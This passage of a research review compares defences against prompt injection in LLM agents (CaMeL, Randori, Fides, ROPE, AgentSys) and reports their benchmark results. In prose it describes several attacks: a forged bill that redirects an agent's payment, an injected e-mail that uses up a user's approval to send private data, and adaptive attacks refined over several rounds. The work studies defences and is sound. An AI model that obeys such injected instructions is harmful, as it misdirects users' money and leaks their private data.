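Endorsement also explains only part of Randori's lead over CaMeL with policies. Three of the 16 tasks require the agent to read a file and act on it, which is impossible without endorsement. Removing endorsement lowered task completion by 12.5 percentage points with Qwen and 10.4 with MiMo. Even without it, Randori with MiMo completed 54.2% of tasks, compared with CaMeL's 37.5%. One likely reason is that Randori has looser policies, as Garby and colleagues acknowledge. For example, its rule for scheduling a payment requires a trusted amount but not a trusted recipient, so a forged bill could redirect the payment without any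 endorsement.

CaMeL without policies let through only five of 622 attacks, so two successful attacks in three runs of 432 is weaker evidence for labels than it may seem. Garby and colleagues also calculate that a perfect score on 47 pairs is compatible with a true resistance rate of about 92%.

In the two attacks that succeeded against CaMeL among the 97 pairs, the planning model had written a small interpreter for the instructions in a file. Whether a pair belongs among the 97 therefore depends on the program the model writes, and another model might write a more permissive one.

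The split also helps interpret other results. TACIT and TypeGuard, the Haskell prototype from Zhou and colleagues, let the model write new code after it has read untrusted text. As Garby and colleagues note, planning first protects neither system, so the systems' own type checks and policies have to stop the attacks in every pair.

### A forged bill in the right file

Two attack runs succeeded against Randori. Both used GPT-5.2 with the same user task and attack, a combination that was run three times. The user asks the agent to read a text file and make the payment it describes, but the attacker has replaced the file's contents with a different payment request. The agent reads the file, extracts the attacker's account number, endorses it and pays, as it would have done with the real bill.

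The real bill and the forged one come from the same file, so the same people could have written either, and both give the same kinds of information in the same format. Their labels are identical because a label records who could have written a text, not who wrote it or whether it is true. Any policy based on these labels must accept both bills or refuse both.

Garby and colleagues write that Randori blocks the attack when it can't use endorsement. This follows from the rule that a payment's recipient must be trusted, which also blocks payment of the real bill. Their test without endorsement adds little evidence, because it used only Qwen and MiMo, which had resisted the attack even with endorsement.

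Size limits don't help either, since the program has to accept an account number that is new to it. The user's decision to delegate justifies the endorsement. By asking the agent to pay the bill in the file, the user authorised it to trust the file, and the endorsement only records this. But the user was presumably thinking of the landlord's bill, not whatever the file might contain by the time the agent opened it.

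A system could do better with more information than the label provides. If it recorded the author of each edit, it could distinguish the landlord's text from a stranger's. It could compare the account number with earlier payments to the same landlord, or check a digital signature on the bill. Each of these helps only in some cases. A first bill from a new supplier has no payment history, for example, and a signature doesn't help if someone has broken into the landlord's account.

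CaMeL's threat model excludes a similar attack. Garby and colleagues go further and say that four independent systems converge on the same remaining cases, which they take as a sign that information-flow defences have reached a limit. That count slightly overstates the overlap, because the forged payment appears in the tests of CaMeL and Randori, while the cases they cite from TACIT and Fides involve only the text of an answer. The argument about identical labels is sound regardless of how many systems have failed this way.

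### Approving a tool or approving a call

When neither the labels nor the plan determines whether an action is allowed, the agent can ask its user. The user's approval then serves as the endorsement or declassification, and its effect depends on exactly what the user approved.

Dongol compares two versions of an agent that answers Alice's e-mail. In each round, the agent reads an e-mail, receives a reply that Alice has approved, and sends it. Its memory also holds private data that the plan never sends. In Tool Approval, each approval allows the next use of the sending tool, whatever the message contains. In Call Approval, each approval allows one message with exactly the contents Alice approved.

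An attacker's e-mail contains an instruction to send the private data, and the model follows it just after Alice has approved her reply but before the agent has sent it.

| | Tool Approval | Call Approval |
|---|---|---|
| The injected message with the private data | The monitor allows it | The monitor refuses it |
| Alice's own reply | The monitor refuses it, because the injection has used up her approval | The agent sends it |

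In the first version, Alice read a harmless reply and approved it, but the attacker used her approval for something else. Any permission that doesn't specify the contents has this weakness. In another of Dongol's examples, a monitor permits one message per run, and an injection uses that permission to send a reset code before the agent can send the planned reply.

Dongol proved that Call Approval eventually sends every reply that Alice approves and nothing else. The proof covers any injection that tries to send messages, provided that the model doesn't go on obeying injections forever. It also assumes that the attacker can see the content and order of messages but not their timing.

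An attacker who can time the messages may learn a little more. If the private data is identical to Alice's reply, the monitor allows the injected message because it matches what she approved. The reply then arrives one step early, so the attacker can infer that the private data matches it. This would rarely matter for a long message, though it might if both were single words such as "yes".

The proof treats Alice's approval as a trusted input that the attacker can't influence. In practice, a model often drafts the reply after reading the e-mail, so an injection can affect the draft. Exact approval guarantees that the agent sends the text Alice saw, but she still has to notice anything wrong with it.

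*Agent libOS* (2026) describes a system in which each approval to release data works once and applies only to a particular agent, recipient and content. An approval for one version of the source data doesn't carry over to a later version. The system may use a model's judgement to block a call or pass it to a person, but never to permit one. It can't control what recipients do with the data.

### Evidence on approval fatigue

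Exact approval interrupts people more often than approving a tool once. If an agent sends 50 e-mails, the user has to read all 50 instead of answering one question. Nearly all of them will be harmless, so the user has little reason to keep reading carefully. Invariant Labs found that many users of Claude Desktop avoid the questions altogether by choosing "Always Allow".

Costa and colleagues warn that repeated approval requests can lead to "confirmation fatigue" and expose users to social engineering, in which an attacker manipulates a person. Microsoft writes that human approval scales poorly and "erodes vigilance". Both claims are plausible, but neither source includes measurements of the effect.

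In Yan's experiment, participants who had told the agent to ask them first often approved actions that went beyond their requests. The agent took only 18 actions, so people can approve the wrong thing even in a short session. This evidence is related to fatigue, but it doesn't show fatigue in the strict sense, in which people become less careful as requests accumulate.

Designers can reduce the number of questions by asking only when labels indicate a problem. Even then, Kolluri and colleagues found that when Fides ran on GPT-5, about a fifth of AgentDojo tasks succeeded only with a person's approval. Designers can also make each question more informative. Microsoft suggests showing where the untrusted data came from, what the agent is about to share, and who would gain access to it.

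Better dialogs should help with attack B, because a user may recognise that an address isn't Bob's. They help less with the forged bill, because a careful user who checked the amount and account number in the dialog against the file would find that they matched.

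## What separation costs in usefulness

When an agent stops to ask for approval, the user can still get the job done. But many of the designs described so far can also fail a task without asking, because a rule forbids the next step or the plan doesn't include it. How often this happens depends on the design, the model, and the tasks the researchers chose for the test.

### Tasks that depend on what the agent reads

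Costa and colleagues, who built Fides, call a task data-independent if the planning model can choose every tool call without seeing what the tools return, and data-dependent if the contents of a result determine which call should come next.

AgentDojo has both data-independent and data-dependent tasks. In one task, a user asks the agent to pay the bill in a named file. This is data-independent because the agent always reads the file and then sends the money, even though the amount and account number vary from bill to bill. In another, a user asks the agent to do everything on a to-do list at a certain web address. This is data-dependent because the list might include sending a message, making a payment or something else.

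A plan written before reading can handle some data-dependent tasks by including a branch for each possibility, as the screen agent of Foerster and colleagues does. This works if the possibilities are few and predictable, but a to-do list can contain any task. A loop that called whichever tool each item required, like the small interpreter that CaMeL's planning model wrote in the banking tests, would let whoever wrote the list control the agent.

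Researchers disagree about how many AgentDojo tasks are of this kind. Costa and colleagues' percentages imply about 20 of the 97, while Li, Wen and colleagues (2026), in *AgentDyn*, count six that need "dynamic planning". Costa and colleagues define these tasks by whether the planning model needs the data to choose its next call, and Li and colleagues by whether an agent could predict the whole sequence of calls from the request. For the user who wanted a new password if a transaction looked suspicious, the decision depends on the data, but the possible steps are easy to predict.

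In *AutoDojo*, Ma, Li and colleagues (2026) sorted the 57 AgentDojo tasks outside the workspace suite by how much the request leaves open. Seventeen requests specify the action and all its details. Another 36 name the action but leave the agent to look up details such as the amount or recipient. Only four leave the action itself open. Most of AgentDojo therefore suits an agent that plans first, so the benchmark probably understates how much usefulness such a design would lose on more open-ended work.

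### What happens when the steps emerge along the way

AgentDyn has 60 open-ended tasks in shopping, GitHub and daily life, with 560 attack cases. An average task takes 7.1 steps, compared with 3.5 in AgentDojo, and the agent has 33 tools instead of 20. Every task also includes at least one helpful instruction from a third party. For example, a bank may respond to a payment request by saying that the amount exceeds $500 and that it has e-mailed a one-time password. The agent then has to find the e-mail and enter the code, although the user mentioned neither.

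The table gives the share of tasks completed without an attack, followed by the attack success rate.

| Design | GPT-4o | Gemini 2.5 Pro | Claude Sonnet 4.5 |
|---|---|---|---|
| No defence | 53.3% / 37.8% | 51.7% / 20.6% | 71.7% / 0.9% |
| Tool Filter | 8.3% / 4.2% | 1.7% / 0.0% | 0.0% / 0.0% |
| CaMeL | 0.0% / 0.0% | 0.0% / 0.0% | 0.0% / 0.0% |
| Progent | 6.7% / 1.7% | 25.0% / 1.6% | 16.7% / 0.2% |
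| DRIFT | 30.0% / 0.8% | 36.7% / 1.1% | 28.3% / 0.2% |

CaMeL completed no tasks with any of the 12 models tested, so its perfect score against attacks is no evidence of protection here. Li and colleagues attribute the failure to its fixed program. Tool Filter failed for a similar reason. It discards tools that seem irrelevant to the request, but the agent often needs them later. Progent can update its rules during a run, but with so many tools its mistakes accumulated until it had blocked almost everything useful. DRIFT did best of the four because it can approve departures from its plan, though it still lost 15 to 43 percentage points in usefulness.

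Although CaMeL scored zero, planning in advance may still work for some of AgentDyn's 60 tasks. Ma and colleagues classify only 12 of them as leaving the action open, and 18 as specifying the action and every detail. In those 18, the unexpected events come from the website or the tool, and a planning model that knew about one-time passwords could write a branch to handle them. Foerster and colleagues made large gains by teaching their planner similar routines for cookie banners. AgentDyn's tasks are also harder for reasons unrelated to planning. With attacks under way, undefended GPT-4o completed every two-step task but only 23.6% of those with more than ten steps.

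Defences that try to ignore instructions had trouble with helpful instructions. With ProtectAI, a detector that screens tool results, no model completed more than 1.7% of tasks. Meta SecAlign, the model trained to resist injections, completed 55.0%, but 9.0% of attacks succeeded. Li and colleagues consider this kind of training a more practical defence, and these results support that view. However, their tests used AgentDojo's stock attack message, and the adaptive attacks of Nasr and colleagues had defeated the same model almost every time.

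The weak attack also makes the Claude Sonnet 4.5 column hard to interpret. Progent lowered utility by 55 percentage points while reducing an attack success rate that was already below 1%. An attack that Li and colleagues adapted to the scenarios succeeded 3.0% of the time against the undefended model, and they acknowledge that stronger attacks may exist.

### Fixing the plan or checking the arguments

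Ma and colleagues tested defences with an attack that improves through trial and error. A separate model writes an injection, receives the number of times it succeeded, and revises it over six rounds. The model isn't given any information about which defence the agent uses.

The tests covered five models on three AgentDojo suites. CaMeL let through at most 1.8% of the attacks, but its task completion rate was 25 to 51 percentage points lower than the undefended agent's. Progent lowered the completion rate by only 4 to 11 points, but let through between 0.5% and 7.7% of the attacks.

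ROPE tracks the origin of each sensitive argument and blocks a tool call if the value came from untrusted content instead of the user. On AgentDyn with GPT-4o-mini, ROPE completed 43.3% of tasks, close to the undefended agent's 46.7%. DRIFT completed 18.3% and Progent 6.7%. The adaptive attack succeeded against ROPE in 2.9% of cases. With Gemini 2.5 Flash, ROPE reduced task completion more, from 36.7% to 25.0%.

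These results suggest that restricting the sequence of calls causes most of the loss in usefulness on AgentDyn, and that checking where arguments come from reduces it much less. But an argument check alone doesn't stop an injection from triggering a call whose sensitive arguments came from the user. On AgentDojo's Slack suite, 11.4% of the adaptive attacks succeeded against ROPE with GPT-4o-mini.

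Open-ended requests are also the most dangerous for an undefended agent. With GPT-4o-mini, the stock attack succeeded in 87.5% of cases where the request left the action open, 63.9% where it left only details open, and 43.3% where it left nothing open. The first figure comes from only 24 cases, but the pattern makes sense, since an agent that has to take instructions from a document has less basis for rejecting an extra one. Progent and DRIFT avoided most of this danger. According to Ma and colleagues, one reason is that these defenses often permit only read-only tools for such requests, so the agent also fails to do what the user asked.

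Another approach lets the planning model respond to results but limits what it sees. *AGENTSYS* (Wen, Xiao and colleagues, 2026) describes a main agent that, before each tool call, declares the form of the answer it will accept, such as a list of names and e-mail addresses. A separate worker model reads the raw result and fills in the form. The main agent reads the completed form and decides what to do next.

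With GPT-4o-mini on all four AgentDojo suites, this agent completed 64.4% of tasks, compared with 63.5% for the undefended agent and 30.0% for CaMeL. The gain over the undefended agent is about one task, so it is safer to say that the design did not reduce task completion. The attack success rate was 0.8%, down from 30.7%.

AgentSys gives up control-flow integrity in return. A name field can hold a sentence, and the main agent will read it. Code checks that the answer is valid JSON, a standard format for structured data, but not that it matches the declared form. When an attacking model repeatedly refined its injections, the attack success rate rose to 2.1% overall and 6.9% in banking. AgentSys is therefore closer to the short hints that Hu and colleagues passed between their two coding agents than to CaMeL.

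AgentDyn, AutoDojo and AgentSys come largely from one group at Washington University in St. Louis, some of whose members also built DRIFT and ROPE. The papers' comparisons of those designs with others need to be repeated independently. Their low scores for CaMeL on small models are easier to trust, because the separate 15-model study also found that CaMeL completed about a quarter of AgentDojo's tasks.

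### Two tests outside the usual pattern

In *The Devil is in the Context*, Chang, Nikolić and colleagues (2026) looked for attacks that existing benchmarks miss. They paired each of AgentDojo's 40 workspace tasks with one random attack. An undefended agent running GPT-5.6 Luna completed every task and resisted every attack.

They then had another model rewrite the cases. Each new attack stayed on the topic of the user's request, applied only under a stated condition, and was meant to change the content of a call or an answer without changing which calls the agent made. Attack B on the meeting notes works similarly. Seven of the 40 new attacks succeeded against the undefended agent and one succeeded against CaMeL. CaMeL completed 11 of the 40 tasks, while PromptArmor, which uses a model to find and delete injected instructions, completed 36 and let three attacks through.

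CaMeL's 11 tasks don't show how much usefulness it lost, because the undefended agent got its perfect score on the original cases, and the rewriting could change the user's request as well as the attack. The comparison with PromptArmor is fairer, but the difference between one attack and three is too small to rank them on security.

*INFUSE* (Nguyen, Guo and colleagues, 2026) tested agents that work through a computer's command line. The benchmark has 40 long tasks, such as debugging a program or deploying a system, and 56 attack scenarios. Across 19 undefended models, another model judged 19.6% of attacks successful. A simplified CaMeL-style control gave little protection, but Nguyen and colleagues caution against generalising from this result.

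That caution is reasonable because these agents have only one tool, which runs a line of text as a command. A single line might read a private file, start another program and contact a server. CaMeL's policies were written for tools with named arguments, such as `recipient`, and a command line has none. A sandbox or a set of narrower tools would make the agents easier to monitor.

### Which costs should shrink as models improve

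Some tasks fail because the model isn't used to the interface. CaMeL's planning model has to write a program for data it hasn't seen, and Fides's has to keep track of hidden variables. These failures should become rarer. In tests by Ma and colleagues, replacing GPT-4o-mini with GPT-5.4-mini doubled the share of tasks that CaMeL completed, from 26.3% to 52.6%, while the undefended agent gained only about 10 percentage points. But a model that does well without a defence may still struggle with one. DeepSeek-v4-Flash completed 89.5% of tasks undefended, the highest share of the five models, but only 38.6% with CaMeL.

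A stronger model can't complete a task if the policy forbids every way of doing it. It may find a permitted route that a weaker model would miss, as Prudentia did when Kolluri and colleagues showed it the labels. But even the strong models of 2026 completed far fewer Slack tasks once ELBA's policies were on.

More precise labels would preserve more of the agent's usefulness. On AgentDyn's web pages, attackers can write only in the advertisements, while the site's own text includes instructions to log in or fill in a form. If one label covers the whole page, the policy has to treat both as hostile. Separate labels would let the agent follow the site's instructions and ignore the advertisements, provided that the site's owner is trustworthy.

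Separation also takes more computation. Wen and colleagues measured the total tokens that GPT-4o-mini used on AgentDojo:

| Design | Tokens (millions) | Compared with no defence |
|---|---|---|
| No defence | 0.82 | 1.0 times |
| DRIFT | 2.37 | 2.9 times |
| Progent | 2.60 | 3.2 times |
| AgentSys | 3.25 | 4.0 times |
| CaMeL | 6.09 | 7.4 times |

Wang and colleagues likewise found that defences acting on an agent's tool calls could cost up to three times as much to run as an undefended agent. Stronger models should need fewer retries, so CaMeL will use fewer tokens, but it will still need the extra calls to a quarantined model or a policy writer. Some of these calls have to wait for others, so the user will still notice a delay even if tokens become very cheap.

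The work required of developers is harder to measure. Ma and colleagues left CaMeL out of their AgentDyn tests because it needs "extensive suite-specific policies", although AgentDyn has only three suites. A company's software changes more often than a benchmark does, so its policies would need more frequent updates. Models can draft labels and policies, and will probably get better at it, but someone who knows the company still has to make decisions such as who may read the salary list.

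Benchmarks rarely count interruptions to the user. Li and colleagues found that agents often stopped to ask for confirmation when a task took an unexpected turn, such as a request for a one-time password. They therefore told every agent to finish without asking. This is sensible when nobody is there to answer, but the scores then don't show how many failed tasks an agent could have completed with a quick reply from the user. Better models should ask fewer unnecessary questions, but they will still have to request the approvals that a policy requires.

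### Tasks that a secure agent should perhaps refuse

Designers of these systems reply that some benchmark tasks require data flows that no secure policy should allow. For example, a user might tell an agent to carry out any instructions in a file that strangers can edit. The defence is right to refuse, but the benchmark counts the refusal as a failure.

Some of AgentDyn's helpful instructions support this reply. In one, an e-mail signed by Bob recommends a website that offers discount coupons to anyone who enters the e-mail address of their shopping account. In another, Alice sends her username and password and asks the user to buy a light bulb through her account. The benchmark treats both messages as genuine, but a phisher could send the same ones. One-time passwords are also a problem, because banks send them partly to confirm that the account holder approves the payment. An agent that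 reads the inbox and enters the code defeats that purpose.

The reply doesn't apply to every failure. AgentDyn also includes tasks such as fetching an invoice from an e-mail attachment or updating a copy of some code before adding to it, and a useful assistant should manage both. People will keep wanting the riskier tasks done, and may switch off a defence that blocks them. Benchmark designers could state in advance which tasks a given policy permits, so that a correct refusal no longer gets the same score as a broken program.

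### Comparisons under the same conditions

Utility scores from different studies are hard to compare because the tasks, models and attacks differ. Each row below comes from one team that ran the same model on the same tasks with and without each defence. Each cell gives the share of tasks completed when there was no attack, followed by the attack success rate. Ma and colleagues used their adaptive attack, and the others used AgentDojo's stock message, so only figures in the same row are comparable.

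| Study and tasks | Model | No defence | CaMeL | Progent | DRIFT |
|---|---|---|---|---|---|
| Wen and colleagues, 97 AgentDojo tasks | GPT-4o-mini | 63.5% / 30.7% | 30.0% / 0.0% | 63.4% / 7.2% | 58.5% / 1.3% |
| Ma and colleagues, 57 AgentDojo tasks | GPT-4o-mini | 66.7% / 52.4% | 26.3% / 0.0% | 63.2% / 7.7% | 49.1% / 6.4% |
| Same | GPT-5.4-mini | 77.2% / 8.7% | 52.6% / 1.8% | 73.7% / 1.5% | 50.9% / 1.0% |
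| Same | Gemini 2.5 Flash | 63.2% / 34.7% | 28.1% / 0.3% | 57.9% / 3.6% | 66.7% / 9.0% |
| Same | DeepSeek-v4-Flash | 89.5% / 16.5% | 38.6% / 0.5% | 78.9% / 4.6% | 59.6% / 2.8% |
| Same | Claude Haiku 4.5 | 70.2% / 1.8% | 40.4% / 0.5% | 63.2% / 0.5% | 45.6% / 1.5% |
| Li and colleagues, 60 AgentDyn tasks | GPT-4o-mini | 46.7% / 50.0% | 0.0% / 0.0% | 6.7% / 10.3% | 18.3% / 3.4% |
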